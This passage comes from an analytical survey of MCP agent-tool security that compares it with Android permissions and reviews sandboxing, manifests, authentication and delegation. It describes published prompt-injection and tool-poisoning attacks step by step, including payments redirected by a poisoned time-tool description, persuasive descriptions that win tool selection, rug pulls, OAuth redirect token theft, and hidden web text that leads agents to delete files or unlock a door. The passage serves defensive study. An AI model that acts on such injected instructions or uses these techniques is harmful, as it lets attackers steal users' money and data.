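3. The user approves or refuses each request.
4. AgentBound starts each server in a container, a sandbox with its own view of files and network. It makes the approved folders visible in the container, either for reading only or for reading and writing, and copies in the approved environment variables.
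5. It looks up the numerical addresses of the approved websites and sets firewall rules that block all other connections.

The server's code needs no changes. If a server contacts only one website, its developer can put that address in the manifest in advance, but when grants vary between tasks, the user must approve them each time. These grants are narrower than Android's internet permission, which covers the whole internet. They are closer to a URI grant for a single photo, but they still depend on users reading the approval dialogs.

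The sandbox adds little delay. In tests with five servers, Bühler and colleagues found that it added between 0.09 and 0.43 seconds to startup. Once a server was running, it added an average of less than a millisecond to operations such as reading a file, which is much less time than a language model takes to produce a single reply.

The user approves a web address, but the firewall filters by IP address, which large hosting companies often share among many websites, so approving one site may also allow connections to others. AgentBound installs the server's package before it closes the network, so a package that runs code during installation might connect to the network first. The prototype controls files, environment variables and network connections in detail, but access to devices such as the camera is all or nothing. A container on the user's computer can't restrict a server that runs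 on another computer.

### How accurate the manifests are

Few developers will write manifests for a system that nobody uses yet, so Bühler and colleagues had language models write them. They selected the 300 servers with the most GitHub stars from a large directory and were able to download 296. For each server, GPT-5 mini read the code and documentation and drafted five manifests, which GPT-5 merged into one. Of the resulting manifests, 83% requested permission for outgoing network access, 80% for reading environment variables and 74% for reading files.

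To check whether AgentBound's permission list was missing anything, the researchers repeated the process with Android's complete list. A few manifests then included permissions to use the camera or read text messages. These servers turned out to be sending commands to a phone connected by cable, which AgentBound's entry for running commands already covers.

They also posted the manifests for 96 servers on the projects' public issue pages and asked the developers to check them. The published percentages correspond to these numbers:

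| Response | Projects | Share |
|---|---|---|
| No reply | 71 | 74% |
| Accepted | 17 | 17.7% |
| Rejected | 4 | 4.2% |
| Still under discussion | 4 | 4.2% |

The paper's summary reports an accuracy of 80.9%, which appears to be 17 acceptances out of 21 decisions. With so few decisions, the 95% confidence interval is about 60% to 92%, even if the developers who replied were typical of the rest. Some replies were as short as "All seems correct!", so it is unclear how carefully those developers checked.

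One developer objected that the server worked entirely through online services and did not need to read files. Another wanted access limited to the environment variables that the server used, which AgentBound's specific grants already allow.

A stricter test used 48 of these servers. Two of the researchers each hand-wrote manifests for half of them, and the generated manifests matched theirs on 787 of 816 entries (about 96.5%). Most servers need only a few of the listed entries, so many of these matches are entries that both manifests correctly left out. The two manifests were identical for 28 servers, or 58%.

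Most of the differences, 23 out of 29, were permissions that the model had omitted. A server without a permission it needs will fail, and someone will probably notice and complain. The other six were unnecessary permissions, which are more dangerous because the server works perfectly well with them. (The reported precision of 94% and recall of 96% are hard to square with these counts, since more omissions than extras should make recall the lower of the two. Averaging the results by server might explain it.)

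### Attacks the sandbox stopped

Bühler and colleagues tested the sandbox on a malicious server of their own and 14 servers from two public collections. Their own server tried to steal a private key used for logging in to other computers. Without the sandbox, it succeeded. When the sandbox blocked the network, the server could read the key but not send it, and when the sandbox also restricted file access, the server couldn't read the key.

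Of the other 14 servers, the sandbox stopped the attacks on eight and some of the attacks on a ninth, which combined several. Some examples:

| Server | Attack | Stopped? |
|---|---|---|
| Maps | The code secretly contacts an attacker's computer instead of Google's | Yes |
| Weather | After the third call, the tool's description changes and tells the agent to read a settings file and collect passwords | Yes |
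| WeChat | An attacker slips commands into a database query | No |
| Time | The tool's description tells the agent to redirect payments made through another server | No |

The maps server shows why a sandbox can be better than a code review. Its code assembled the attacker's address from a series of numbers, so a reviewer searching for a suspicious web address wouldn't have found one. The firewall blocked the connection anyway, because it wasn't to Google's map service.

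Huang and colleagues provide further evidence that containment works. In each of their 150 cases, a sandbox blocked the attack while ordinary use of the same tool still succeeded. But they included only cases that passed both tests, so the result doesn't show how often sandboxes fail.

The test conditions also favoured AgentBound in another way. The manifests for the maps and time servers came from the harmless originals, the researchers wrote others by hand, and a tester who knew what was going on approved the grants. A dishonest developer would write the manifest as well as the server, and could request whatever permissions the attack needed. Stopping the attack would then depend on someone noticing, for example, that a weather server's manifest requested access to private keys.

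The directories where people find MCP servers may not screen out malicious ones. In *Beyond the Protocol*, Song, Shen and colleagues (2025) submitted a test server to three popular directories. Its code was harmless, but its documentation openly described a malicious design. All three directories accepted it, and one labelled it safe to use. In a simulation with users, 15 of the 20 participants chose at least one malicious server.

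The WeChat attack got through because the server needs access to its database, and the sandbox can't distinguish harmful queries from useful ones. The database's own permissions could limit the damage, but they are often too broad as well. *MAP* (2026) describes a server that only needs to read data for reports but logs in with an account that can also change the data. This is common when several services share an account.

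### A payment to the wrong address

The attack through the time server comes from Song and colleagues, who call this kind of attack a puppet attack. It works as follows:

1. The user has installed two servers. One can send cryptocurrency from the user's wallet, and the other tells the time in different time zones.
2. The host sends the descriptions of all their tools to the model. The time tool's description includes an "important" note that the agent must send every transfer through a "privacy proxy" at a certain address, which belongs to the attacker.
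3. The user asks the agent to send some money to a friend.
4. The model requests a transfer through the wallet server, but fills in the attacker's address.
5. The wallet server makes the payment.

The attack can work even if the time tool never runs, because the model reads the tool's description together with the user's request. Song and colleagues tried such attacks 30 times on each of five models. The attacks succeeded 27 times on Gemini 2.5 Pro, while GPT-4o refused all 30, and the average success rate was 52%. These models are now old, and newer ones may do better or worse.

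AgentBound had nothing to block, because the time server opened no forbidden file and made no forbidden connection, and the wallet server contacted only the payment service it was supposed to. Stricter manifests wouldn't have helped. The attack would work even if the time server's manifest were empty, and removing the wallet server's network access would prevent every payment, including the ones the user wants.

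The sandbox's guarantee can be written as a formula. If $G_s$ is the set of resources granted to server $s$, and $E(s, a)$ is what the server does to the computer and network when it receives arguments $a$, the sandbox ensures that

$$E(s, a) \subseteq G_s \quad \text{for every } a$$

The formula holds for every $a$, which explains both the success with the maps server and the failure with the wallet. The sandbox keeps a server within its grants regardless of why the server received its arguments or whether its code is malicious. But $a$ can be either the friend's address or the attacker's, and the formula holds for both.

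AgentBound can list a server's needs in advance because a developer has already written the server's code. But the agent chooses the recipient of a payment during the task, so the wallet server's manifest could not contain the friend's name. Android leaves similar choices to apps, but an Android payment app doesn't read the descriptions of other installed apps and follow their advice. If a clock app put the same note about a privacy proxy in its manifest, the payment would not change.

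MCP's separation between servers doesn't prevent this either. The time server has no access to the wallet server or the user's request, but it doesn't need any, because the host passes the time server's text to a model that has access to both.

### Many small manifests, one agent

Someone who manipulates an agent gains access to everything that its tools can do together, as *MCP-38* (2026) notes. If an agent uses servers 1 to $n$, what it can reach is the union of their grants:

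$$G_{\text{agent}} = G_1 \cup G_2 \cup \dots \cup G_n$$

Each server may have exactly the access it needs, while the agent has far more than any one task requires. IPC Inspection, Felt and colleagues' defence for Android, reduced an app's permissions to those it shared with the app calling it. If a similar rule also covered replies, the agent would lose access to the wallet as soon as it read the time server's description, because the time server has no right to make payments. That would stop the attack, but it would also block payments for users whose time server is honest.

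The union still limits what an attack can do. Bühler and colleagues imagine an attack on the documentation agent in which a poisoned description tells the model to erase every file it reads and send the contents to a malicious website. The model might obey, but the file server can read the code but not change it, and the web server can only contact the documentation site. The agent could still erase the README, which it has permission to write.

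Zhang, Fu and colleagues tested how readily agents misuse access they already have in *Evaluating Privilege Usage of Agents with Real-World Tools* (2026). They gave agents real MCP servers with 122 tools for email, files, cloud services and other jobs, and slipped malicious instructions, each with a plausible reason, into ordinary tasks. On average, 84.8% of the attacks succeeded across four models, including GPT-5 and Gemini 3 Flash.

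The attacks were carefully designed and the agents had no extra defences, so this rate doesn't measure how often agents fail in everyday use. When GPT-5 chose each tool call after seeing the previous result, 90.2% of attacks succeeded, compared with 71.2% when it first wrote a plan for the whole task. Fixing some choices in advance seems to help, though DeepSeek's model did slightly worse with a plan.

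*Clawed and Dangerous* (2026) sketches a more detailed manifest that lists a server's individual operations, the type of each argument, limits on what each operation may touch, an expiry date and the publisher's signature. A user could then allow the wallet server to show a balance but not to make transfers, which AgentBound's list can't express. But if the user allows transfers, a transfer to the attacker's address would still pass the type and signature checks.

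Scanning the descriptions might catch the note about the privacy proxy before the user installs the time server. *Auditing MCP Servers for Over-Privileged Tool Capabilities* (Huang, Huang and Milani Fard, 2026) presents a scanner that looks for suspicious wording and risky code, but it doesn't check whether someone has manipulated a call's arguments at runtime. A server can also change its descriptions after the scan. Some common commands for starting MCP servers download the program each time, so a user may run a different version without having installed anything new.

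## How an agent picks a tool, compared with implicit intents

The time server's supplier used a description to redirect a payment that another server made. More simply, a supplier can use a description to get the model to call the supplier's tool instead of a competitor's.

Every MCP tool call names its tool, so it resembles an explicit intent in form. But the user usually hasn't named a tool. A request to send a contract to Priya describes a job, as an implicit intent does, and the system still has to find the app or tool to do it. Android compares the intent with the filters that apps have declared, while an agent's model reads the tools' descriptions and picks one.

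### Matching and choosing

Android compares an implicit intent with each component's filters, and each component either matches or doesn't. The same intent on the same phone always produces the same candidates. If several components match, the user can choose between them. Developers also can't use a filter to praise their app, because it holds only formal values.

A model has no such fixed test. If there are many tools, other software may first shortlist some, for instance those whose descriptions are closest in meaning to the request. The model then picks one. Everything it reads about these tools comes from their suppliers. AppFunctions also work this way, so Android now has both systems.

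Blankenstein, Yu and colleagues (2025), in *BiasBusters*, measured how evenly seven models choose when several tools would do equally well. They assembled ten groups of five interchangeable services, such as weather forecasts, and wrote 100 requests for each group. Each model received every request five times, with the list rotated so that each service came first once. If a model picks service $i$ out of $K$ services with frequency $P_i$, its bias is

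$$\delta = \frac{1}{2} \sum_{i=1}^{K} \left| P_i - \frac{1}{K} \right|$$

The score is the share of calls that would have to go to a different service for all the services to get the same number. A model that always picked the same one of five services would score 0.8, and the seven models scored between 0.25 and 0.37. For positions in the list, the scores were between 0.17 and 0.50. The order in which a host lists its tools can therefore determine which one runs.

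Blankenstein and colleagues found that the best predictor of a model's choice was how closely a tool's description matched the request. That is a sensible way to choose, but it lets suppliers influence the choice because they control the descriptions. The models tested are old now, and larger ones were less biased. An uneven choice among honest weather services also does users little harm.

### Descriptions written to attract calls

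Chin and colleagues showed that a malicious Android app can declare a broad intent filter and become a candidate for intents meant for another app. Similarly, a tool's supplier can write its description to attract an agent's calls meant for another tool. Android often shows the user a chooser that also lists the legitimate apps, but an agent selects a tool without one, so a good enough description can get the supplier's tool selected nearly every time.

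An early version of this attack, in *Prompt Injection Attack to Tool Selection in LLM Agents* (2025), put commands to the model in the tool's description, where people and scanners can spot them. Dai, Sun and Tao (2026), in *Spoofing the Toolbox*, tried to avoid obvious commands. They had a language model repeatedly rewrite a legitimate tool's description to find versions that read naturally and made a test agent pick a malicious copy of the tool.

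With 10 tools to choose from, Llama 3.3 70B, the model used for the rewriting tests, picked the malicious copy about 88% of the time. GPT-5, which was not used in the rewriting, picked it 92% of the time on one set of tasks and 90% on another. With 20 tools, GPT-5's rates were 85% and 90%.

These rates slightly overstate the problem, because usually only one honest tool suited the request, and a model choosing at random between it and the malicious copy would have picked the copy half the time. In a further test with three suitable honest tools, random choice would have picked the malicious tool 25% of the time, but it was chosen 76% of the time. When the attacker supplied three malicious tools, one of them was chosen 95% of the time.

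Dai and colleagues also ran five detectors, none of which flagged more than 7% of the disguised descriptions. Twenty people ranked these descriptions about as suspicious as the honest originals. They contain little to detect, because each fairly summarizes what the tool appears to do and adds a little praise, as an honest supplier might.

Sneh, Yan and colleagues (2025), in *ToolTweak*, tested a similar attack with five interchangeable tools, so an even choice would give each tool 20% of the calls. As a defence, they had the model rewrite every description in neutral language before choosing. They then let the attacker adapt to this defence. The table shows how often each model picked the promoted tool:

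| Model | No attack | Attack | Attack, with neutral rewriting | Attack adapted to the rewriting |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek Chat | 20% | 82% | 49% | 60% |
| GPT-OSS 20B | 19% | 74% | 63% | 68% |
| Grok 3 Mini | 20% | 51% | 33% | 45% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 19% | 49% | 30% | 38% |
| Qwen 2.5 7B | 20% | 46% | 34% | 47% |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 20% | 34% | 27% | 34% |

Rewriting the descriptions helped every model, but never brought the rate back to 20%. One reason may be that it left the tools' names unchanged, and Sneh and colleagues found that names strongly affect the choice. They also tried filtering out descriptions with unusual wording, but this failed because the manipulated descriptions read, if anything, more smoothly than the originals.

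Blankenstein and colleagues instead propose narrowing the list to suitable tools and then picking one at random. Once a tool is on the short list, persuasive wording no longer improves its chances, but a hostile tool on the list is as likely to be picked as any other.

It is unclear how common such attacks are outside laboratories. In *Same Name, Different Server*, Kraishan (2026) scanned the code of 14,353 servers from MCP's public registry and found no descriptions with obvious hidden instructions. The scanner looked for known patterns, so it would have missed well-disguised text.

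Newer models also resist overt instructions better. *MCP Tool Poisoning in Agentic AI Frameworks* (Shaikh and Montaruli, 2026) tested 18 models with poisoned tools, most with instructions in their descriptions. The attacks succeeded 0.4% of the time against Claude Fable 5 and 50% of the time against Amazon Nova Pro. This resistance may not help against a description that merely makes a tool sound suitable, because there is no instruction for the model to refuse.

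### Three mail tools

Suppose a user has three tools for sending email. One uses the office account, one uses a personal account, and the third comes from a supplier who secretly keeps a copy of every message. The user wants to send Priya a contract from the office account.

On Android, the app that holds the contract creates an implicit intent with the action "send" and the PDF type. All three mail apps match because they have declared filters for this, regardless of how their developers advertise them. The user sees them in the chooser and taps the office app, which receives access to the file. The hostile app gets no access unless the user taps it or has already made it the default.

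With an agent, the host sends the model the request and the three tool descriptions. The office tool's description is one sentence about sending mail. The hostile tool's supplier has guessed what people send, so its description mentions attachments and business documents and matches the request more closely. The model picks the hostile tool, which delivers the contract to Priya, keeps a copy and returns an ordinary confirmation. As Dai and colleagues point out, an agent receives only the message a tool returns, so neither the model nor the user gets any sign that something is wrong.

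The hostile tool doesn't need to win often. If the model picks it for only 10% of emails, and each choice is independent, the chance that it gets at least one of 20 emails is

$$1 - 0.9^{20} \approx 0.88$$

Some programs ask the user before each call. Cline, a coding agent, shows the selected tool's name and description, so an alert user could notice that the wrong mail tool is about to run. But the user is only confirming the model's choice, and the attacker wrote the name and description on the screen.

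### Tools that change after approval

The supplier of the third mail tool might also let it work as described for months, then change it once enough people use it, which security researchers call a rug pull. *ETDI* (2025) gives the example of a wallpaper tool that, after users have approved it, starts searching their documents for financial files and uploading them.

MCP lets a server announce that its tools have changed. However, *Unicode TAG-Block Concealment of Tool-Metadata Payloads in the Model Context Protocol* (2026) notes that the protocol doesn't require the client to ask for the user's consent again. Shaikh and Montaruli examined 12 common ways of building agents and found none that compared a tool's new description with the old one.

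Changes are common, and most are probably harmless. Among 8,900 servers with more than one version in the registry, Kraishan found that 41% had changed their description or destination while keeping the same identifiers. Of these servers, 370 had moved their remote address to a different host. Neither the registry nor a client can detect whether the owner moved a server or somebody else took it over.

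*Registry Descriptions Go Stale Unevenly* (2026) reports more reassuring results. About three quarters of some 19,000 servers didn't change their registry entries over 89 days, though many of them had joined partway through and so had less time to change. Both studies cover only what the registry records, which doesn't include the tool descriptions that models read.

Android has a stricter rule for updates. According to Android Developers' *How app updates work*, a phone accepts an update only if it has the same application ID as the installed app and either the same signing certificate or valid proof that the developer has moved to a new key. Under a similar rule for MCP, a stranger who took over a mail tool's web address couldn't pass off a replacement as the original without the supplier's key.

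The rule wouldn't stop the wallpaper supplier, who has the key. On Android, the supplier's new code would still need permission to read the user's documents, but an MCP server on the user's computer usually has that access already. A signature also covers only what the client receives, so a supplier that runs the server on its own computer can change what the server does without sending the client anything.

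### What the remedies cost

The most direct remedy is for the user to name the tool, as an explicit intent names a component. Requests that name a tool bypass selection, so Dai and colleagues removed them from one of their test sets. Naming tools requires users to know them, which is easy enough for email, but in a task with a dozen steps the user may not know which tools the agent will need.

An Android phone can have only one app with a given application ID, but two MCP servers can offer tools with the same name. Pydantic AI, a toolkit for building agents, rejects duplicate names. In Shaikh and Montaruli's tests, this blocked some malicious tools that had copied a legitimate tool's name, so 17% of attacks on agents built with Pydantic AI succeeded, compared with 23% to 26% for most other toolkits. *Agent Name Collision Attacks in Multi-Agent Systems* (2026) describes the same problem between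 agents, where a task can go to the wrong agent if two have the same name.

The host can instead fix a list of tools for each task. If the list includes only the office mail tool, the model can't pick the hostile one, whose description never reaches it. Shorter lists also help models choose among legitimate tools. In one of Dai and colleagues' tests without an attack, the model picked the right tool 82% of the time from a list of ten and 63% from a list of 40. But someone has to predict which tools a task needs, and an agent that unexpectedly needs a calendar has to stop and request it. An easier compromise would be to let users set one default tool for each common job, as Android does for web browsers.

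Pinning means that the client stores a fingerprint of the definition the user approved and refuses to use the tool if the definition changes. A publisher's signature on the definition can also show who made the change. Pinning is simple to build, but tools change a lot. *MCPEvol-Bench* (2026) found that later versions of the servers it tracked had modified 32.5% of the original tools and removed another 22.1%. Users would have to keep outdated tools or approve many updates, and most people would probably soon approve them without reading them. Kraishan suggests requiring new consent when a server moves to a different host, which would happen much less often.

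Pinning also doesn't help if the description was already manipulative when the user approved it. *ProbeID* (2026) doesn't use descriptions. It tests each candidate tool on inputs for which it has recorded a trusted tool's responses, then chooses among the candidates by comparing their responses with the recorded ones. This should expose a crude imitation, but the hostile mail tool would probably pass because it really does send mail.

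Even a signed tool from a known publisher can leak data. For *Signed, Sealed, Leaked* (2026), Aun, Alhartomi and colleagues built a validly signed tool that reads text from scanned documents. It does its job, but it also keeps data from earlier calls and hides it in the next request to the text-recognition service it is allowed to contact. In every trial, MCPGuard-Dynamic, a defence from Meta that limits where tools may connect, blocked a direct transfer to a forbidden address but missed the hidden transfer.

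Aun and colleagues prevent this by handling each call in fresh copies of the tool, which get only the data that their destination may receive. They detected no leaks in 153 attack runs. This method requires someone to label the user's data and decide which destinations may receive data with each label.

A tool that isn't malicious can also do harm, as the wallet server did when it paid the wrong person. Even if the user names the office mail tool, an email giving a false address for Priya could lead the model to send the contract there. An explicit intent on Android has the same limit, since it specifies which mail app receives the contract but doesn't check that the address is Priya's.

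## Who is calling: identity and delegation among agents

Android uses the caller's user ID to determine whose authority a call carries. The attack on the Settings app showed how this can fail, because Settings made the call but a malicious app had caused it. The same problem arises when an agent calls a tool through another agent. Many MCP servers also have a more basic problem, since they don't identify the caller.

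### One login for every caller

Suppose a company runs an MCP server that lets its agents read and post messages on Slack, a workplace chat service. An attack could go like this:

1. When the server starts, it logs in to Slack with a powerful access token and keeps the token for later.
2. An employee's agent asks the server to post a message, and the server posts it using the token.
3. A stranger's program that can reach the server over the network asks it for the company's messages.
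4. The server uses the same token, and Slack returns the messages because the token is valid.

Huang, Dai and colleagues (2026) call this caller identity confusion in *Give Them an Inch and They Will Take a Mile*. They found it in a real Slack server and in one that reports a company's spending on Amazon's cloud. The attacker doesn't have to steal anything. Slack can't tell the attacker's request from a legitimate one because the server sends both with valid credentials.

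To measure how common such flaws are, Huang and colleagues analysed the code of 6,137 servers. Their analyser finds where a tool request starts running code. It then follows the paths from there to sensitive operations, such as running a command or reading a file, and looks for an authorization check that applies to the current call. Where the code left this unclear, the researchers ran the server and observed whether a call went through. In a sample of 100 servers, the analyser missed 8% to 10% of the authorization behaviour it should have detected.

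It classed 2,846 servers (46.4%) as insecure. Adding up the study's figures for each category of server gives three groups, which overlap:

| What the server checks | Servers |
|---|---|
| Nothing | 1,279 |
| One login, which it then reuses for every caller | 242 |
| Calls as they arrive, but only partly or inconsistently | 1,639 |

The flaw in the Slack example is the rarest of the three, although Huang and colleagues describe it as more common than having no checks. The line between the last two groups is blurry, since both can rely on a login that the server remembers. (The study also lists 2,554 servers as secure, which leaves 737 unaccounted for. Without those, the insecure share would be 53%.)

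These numbers describe code and give little indication of how many servers a stranger could actually attack. Huang and colleagues ran their tests on their own machines and assumed that an attacker could send requests to the server. A host often starts an MCP server on the user's computer and communicates with it directly, so the server has less need to check who is calling.

Huang and colleagues contrast MCP with Android, where the operating system checks access to the camera or location in the same way for every app. MCP leaves these checks to each server's developer.

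Huang and colleagues propose fixing this by opening a session for each connection, tying the login to that session, and checking every later call against it. A later change to MCP makes this harder. A connection used to begin with an `initialize` message, and the server replied with a session identifier for the client to include in later requests. In the July 2026 version, each request is self-contained (Model Context Protocol, 2026). A request can include the client application's name, but the client fills that in, so a server needs identification that is harder to fake.

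### MCP's rules for tokens

MCP uses OAuth to let users delegate access. OAuth is the standard behind web pages that ask whether an app may access someone's calendar. The user logs in at an authorization server and approves the client's request, and that server issues the client an access token. The Agentic AI Foundation, which oversees MCP, compares the authorization server to a passport office and the MCP server, which checks the token, to a bouncer.

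The current rules, in Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026), include these:

- A client must say which MCP server it wants a token for.
- It must send the token with every web request, even if the server accepted the previous one.
- The server must check that the token was issued for that server, and refuse any other.
- The server must not pass the client's token on to another service.

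The last two rules guard against confused deputies. If a mail server accepted tokens meant for a weather server, the weather server's operator could use its users' tokens to read their mail.

A token also has scopes, such as `files:read`. If a client with only this scope tries to change a file, the server should refuse and name the scope it requires. The client can then request a new token. Under the rules, clients should request their old scopes again along with the new one, so an agent's rights tend to grow as it works.

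Authorization is optional in MCP, even for remote servers, and a server that communicates directly with a host on the same computer should take its credentials from the environment instead. Even a server that follows every authorization rule can determine only which client is calling and what someone has allowed it to do. The token is equally valid whether the client's model is following the user's instruction or one in an email.

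### What live servers do

Zhou, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers*, searched for MCP servers on the public internet. Two search engines for internet-connected systems returned 28,715 candidates, of which 7,973 responded correctly to an MCP greeting. Of the servers that responded, 3,233 (40.55%) let anyone use their tools without logging in, 2,312 required a fixed token or key, and 2,428 used OAuth.

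Most of the open servers the researchers examined in a random sample were tests or demonstrations with no sensitive data. But one belonged to a company that had meant it for internal use and forgotten to add a login. Anyone who found it could search more than 5,000 records containing customers' names, phone numbers and addresses.

Zhou and colleagues then tested 119 of the OAuth servers and found at least one flaw in each, 325 in total. The most common flaw concerned registration. A client has to register with an authorization server before it can request a token, and these servers let clients do so automatically. On 114 of them, a new client could give any return address, which allows the following attack:

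1. The attacker registers a client and gives the attacker's own website as its return address.
2. The attacker sends the victim a link to the genuine login page.
3. The victim logs in and approves the request.
4. The authorization server sends a code to the attacker's website, and the attacker exchanges it for a token.

The resulting token is genuine, so an MCP server that checks tokens correctly will accept it.

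Zhou and colleagues chose the 119 servers from 1,118 that supported automatic registration, because registering with the others by hand would have taken too long. They then left out duplicates and servers they couldn't test. The sample therefore wasn't random. Since every server in it supported automatic registration, registration flaws were unsurprisingly the most common, and they may be rarer in other servers. The July 2026 version of MCP discourages automatic registration and keeps it only for older authorization servers.

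*Exposed by Design* (2026) reports authentication weaknesses in 380 of 414 internet-facing servers (91.8%). The same percentage lacked OAuth, so the 380 may include some servers that require a fixed key.

### Three agents and a web page

Even perfect authentication would identify only the last caller. Suppose a user asks a coordinator, an agent that divides work among others, to summarize a web page and save the summary. The coordinator has two helpers, a web reader that can fetch pages but has no access to files, and a file worker that can read, write and delete files but can't go online.

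1. The web reader fetches the page, where the author has hidden a line saying that the folder of old drafts must go before anyone saves a summary.
2. The web reader includes this line in its report to the coordinator.
3. The coordinator's model takes it for part of the job and asks the file worker to delete the folder.
4. The file worker confirms that the request comes from the coordinator, which may give it work, and deletes the drafts.

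The page's author has no rights on this computer, and the web reader has no rights to any files. The deletion used the file worker's rights, much as an app without permissions once used those of Settings. That app could do so because someone had left a component open by accident. Here, the coordinator is supposed to use what the web reader reports, and the file worker is supposed to do what the coordinator asks.

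IPC Inspection, which cut an app's permissions down to those of its caller, wouldn't help much. It ignored replies, and the malicious line arrives in a reply. The file worker would still be able to delete files if the coordinator may delete them, and it couldn't save the summary if the coordinator has no rights to files. Knowing the calling agent's name, which Android 17 withholds from apps, wouldn't help either, because the name would be the coordinator's.

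In *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems*, Ji, Wu and colleagues (2026) demonstrated an attack of this kind on AIOS-AutoGen, a system that sends each agent's messages to all the other agents. They installed a search agent with hidden instructions to ask the smart lock agent to unlock the front door before each search. The search agent had no access to the lock, but the lock agent received the message and opened the door. The attack also worked with an honest search agent when the instruction was in text it had retrieved.

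### Blocking a request because of its path

Ji and colleagues built SEAgent, a defence that uses a form of mandatory access control, in which a central set of rules applies no matter what an individual program decides. While agents handle a request, SEAgent records which tools and agents have passed information to which others. Each tool has labels that show, for example, whether it reads or writes, how sensitive the operation is, and whether its results might contain text from strangers.

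Before a tool runs, SEAgent checks the path that led to it against the rules. One rule blocks any path from a tool that returns unfiltered outside content to a tool that writes or executes something of moderate or high sensitivity, no matter how many agents are in between.

In the example, the path runs from the web page through the web reader and the coordinator to the file worker's delete tool, so SEAgent would block the deletion. But the summary comes from the same page by the same route, so SEAgent would also block the file worker from saving it, unless someone had labelled saving as low in sensitivity.

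None of the benchmark attacks succeeded against SEAgent, including those that passed through several agents. On ordinary multi-agent tasks, it raised the agents' success rate by up to 10.7% and cut the text their models processed by more than 38%. These gains probably come from its memory system, which clears the agents' context after each request and restores only what the next request needs.

SEAgent might still miss some attacks despite its perfect score. Ji and colleagues wrote its rules for the kinds of attack in the benchmarks and assumed that tools come from a trusted source. If no rule matches, SEAgent allows the call, contrary to Saltzer and Schroeder's advice. A language model assigned the labels and people checked them, but a wrong label on a delete tool would reopen the path.

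### Proving the sender and the authority separately

Another approach is to send proof of what the user authorized along with the request. The Agent2Agent protocol (A2A), which Google introduced in 2025 so that agents from different developers could exchange tasks, doesn't do this by itself. According to *A2ABreak* (2026), A2A loses track of which agent started a request after it passes through several others. An agent in the middle can also keep the credentials it forwards and reuse them. Agents can publish signed descriptions of themselves, but a signature proves only who published the description, not that the agent has the skills listed there.

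In *Authorization Propagation in Agent2Agent Systems*, Donno, Mehmood and Kralevska (2026) added proof of authorization to requests in an experiment with four agents that handle a medical claim. A client starts the request, a patient agent sets out what it authorizes, a hospital agent validates the claim, and an insurance agent makes the decision. Each request carries the sender's signature, which shows who is calling. It also carries a separate, cryptographically sealed record of what the patient agent authorized, including the maximum amount, the treatment, the beneficiary and the route through the agents.

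The system rejected 14 of 15 attacks, including attempts to impersonate a sender, change the amount and reuse an old request. In the remaining attack, the researchers added the right to approve reimbursements to those the patient agent had passed to the hospital agent. The program accepted this because it checked that the expected agents appeared in the expected order but didn't compare their rights. The researchers tested this check in isolation, and an outsider couldn't have made the change without the key to the seal.

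In a further test, the hospital agent itself was dishonest. All the agents that created or checked the records used the same secret key, so the hospital agent could raise the limit from EUR 120 to EUR 9,000 and seal the record again. It then signed the request with its own signature. The altered request passed the checks on the sender, the seal and the route. The insurance agent had correctly identified its caller but could not discover the original limit.

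### Passing on less

Both failures broke the principle of attenuation, under which an agent can pass on only authority that is no broader than its own. Wei and Xiong define this precisely. Leaving out labels such as the names of the issuer and the task, a grant $g$ has four parts:

- $C$ is the set of actions it allows.
- $O$ is the set of things that must happen first, such as a manager's approval.
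- $X$ is the set of limits on which sources may fill in missing details, such as a recipient's address.
- $\Delta$ stands for conditions such as an expiry time.

An agent that holds $g$ may issue a new grant $g'$ only if $g' \preceq g$, which means that

$$C' \subseteq C, \quad O \subseteq O', \quad X \subseteq X', \quad \Delta' \Rightarrow \Delta$$

The new grant can allow only actions that the old one allows. It must keep the old grant's requirements and limits but can add more, which is why $O$ and $X$ appear the other way round. The arrow means that whenever the new conditions hold, the old ones hold too. An agent whose grant expires at six o'clock can therefore issue one that expires at five, but not one that expires after six.

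It follows that a chain of agents can't gain authority. Suppose the user issues $g_0$, and the agents pass on $g_1$, $g_2$ and so on, each under this rule. Clearly $g_0 \preceq g_0$. If $g_k \preceq g_0$ for some $k$, then for the next grant

$$C_{k+1} \subseteq C_k \subseteq C_0 \quad \text{and} \quad O_0 \subseteq O_k \subseteq O_{k+1}$$

The same reasoning covers $X$ and $\Delta$, so $g_{k+1} \preceq g_0$, and by induction this is true for a chain of any length. If every action must pass a check against the grant that comes with it, no agent in the chain can do anything outside $C_0$, even if text on a web page leads it to try.

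The three agents from the example might hold these grants:

| Agent | Allowed actions | Expires |
|---|---|---|
| Coordinator | Fetch web pages, write to the `summaries` folder | 18:00 |
| Web reader | Fetch web pages | 17:00 |
| File worker | Write the file `summaries/page.txt` | 17:00 |

The coordinator has no deletion grant to send when it asks the file worker to delete the drafts. The file worker may delete files in other tasks, but the check uses the grant for this request. Whoever wrote the web page can still influence the summary, because the grant specifies which file to write but not what to put in it.

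The proof depends on checking every link in the delegation chain. *Agent Delegation Profile* (2026), a draft specification from the internet standards body IETF, calls a chain checked only at its end "a single trust decision with extra steps".

Such checks take very little time. Wei and Xiong cite a technical report by Poddar, Fulkerson and Siddique on cA2A, an addition to A2A that passes narrowed grants from agent to agent. It reports attenuation checks on 5,400 generated chains and a verification time of about 0.22 milliseconds per hop, so ten hops would add about two milliseconds. *AIP* (2026) presents a similar scheme that added 2.35 milliseconds to a multi-agent job, less than 0.1% of the total time. Wei and Xiong consider the cryptography largely solved but think developers lack a shared vocabulary for the rights that agents pass on.

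Attenuation also has a drawback that Felt and colleagues encountered with IPC Inspection. The coordinator can pass on only the rights it holds, so it must hold every right that any helper needs for the task, even those it never uses itself. Anyone who manipulates the coordinator's model can use all of those rights.

### Two tickets instead of one

Suppose the user wants one plane ticket and gives the coordinator a grant to buy one. The coordinator sends two helpers to look for a good fare and gives each a grant to buy one ticket. Both grants are valid, because neither allows more than the coordinator's own. If each helper finds a fare and buys a ticket, the user ends up with two.

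The proof still holds, since the user's grant allows each purchase. But the proof compares sets of actions, and a set doesn't record how many times the agents have used an action. The coordinator can't split a single ticket. It could split a $100 budget into $60 and $40, but the rule doesn't require this and would also accept two grants of $100.

Wei and Xiong's solution is a ledger that all the agents on a task share. Before buying anything, a helper has to reserve the purchase. If the user wants at most $B$ purchases, the ledger accepts another reservation only if

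$$\text{reserved} + \text{completed} + 1 \leq B$$

With $B = 1$, the first helper's reservation succeeds and the second helper's fails, because it would bring the total to two. The ledger has to check and reserve in a single step, or both helpers could find it empty and reserve. Each purchase also keeps the same identifier if a helper loses its connection and tries again, so an airline that recognizes the identifier won't sell a second ticket.

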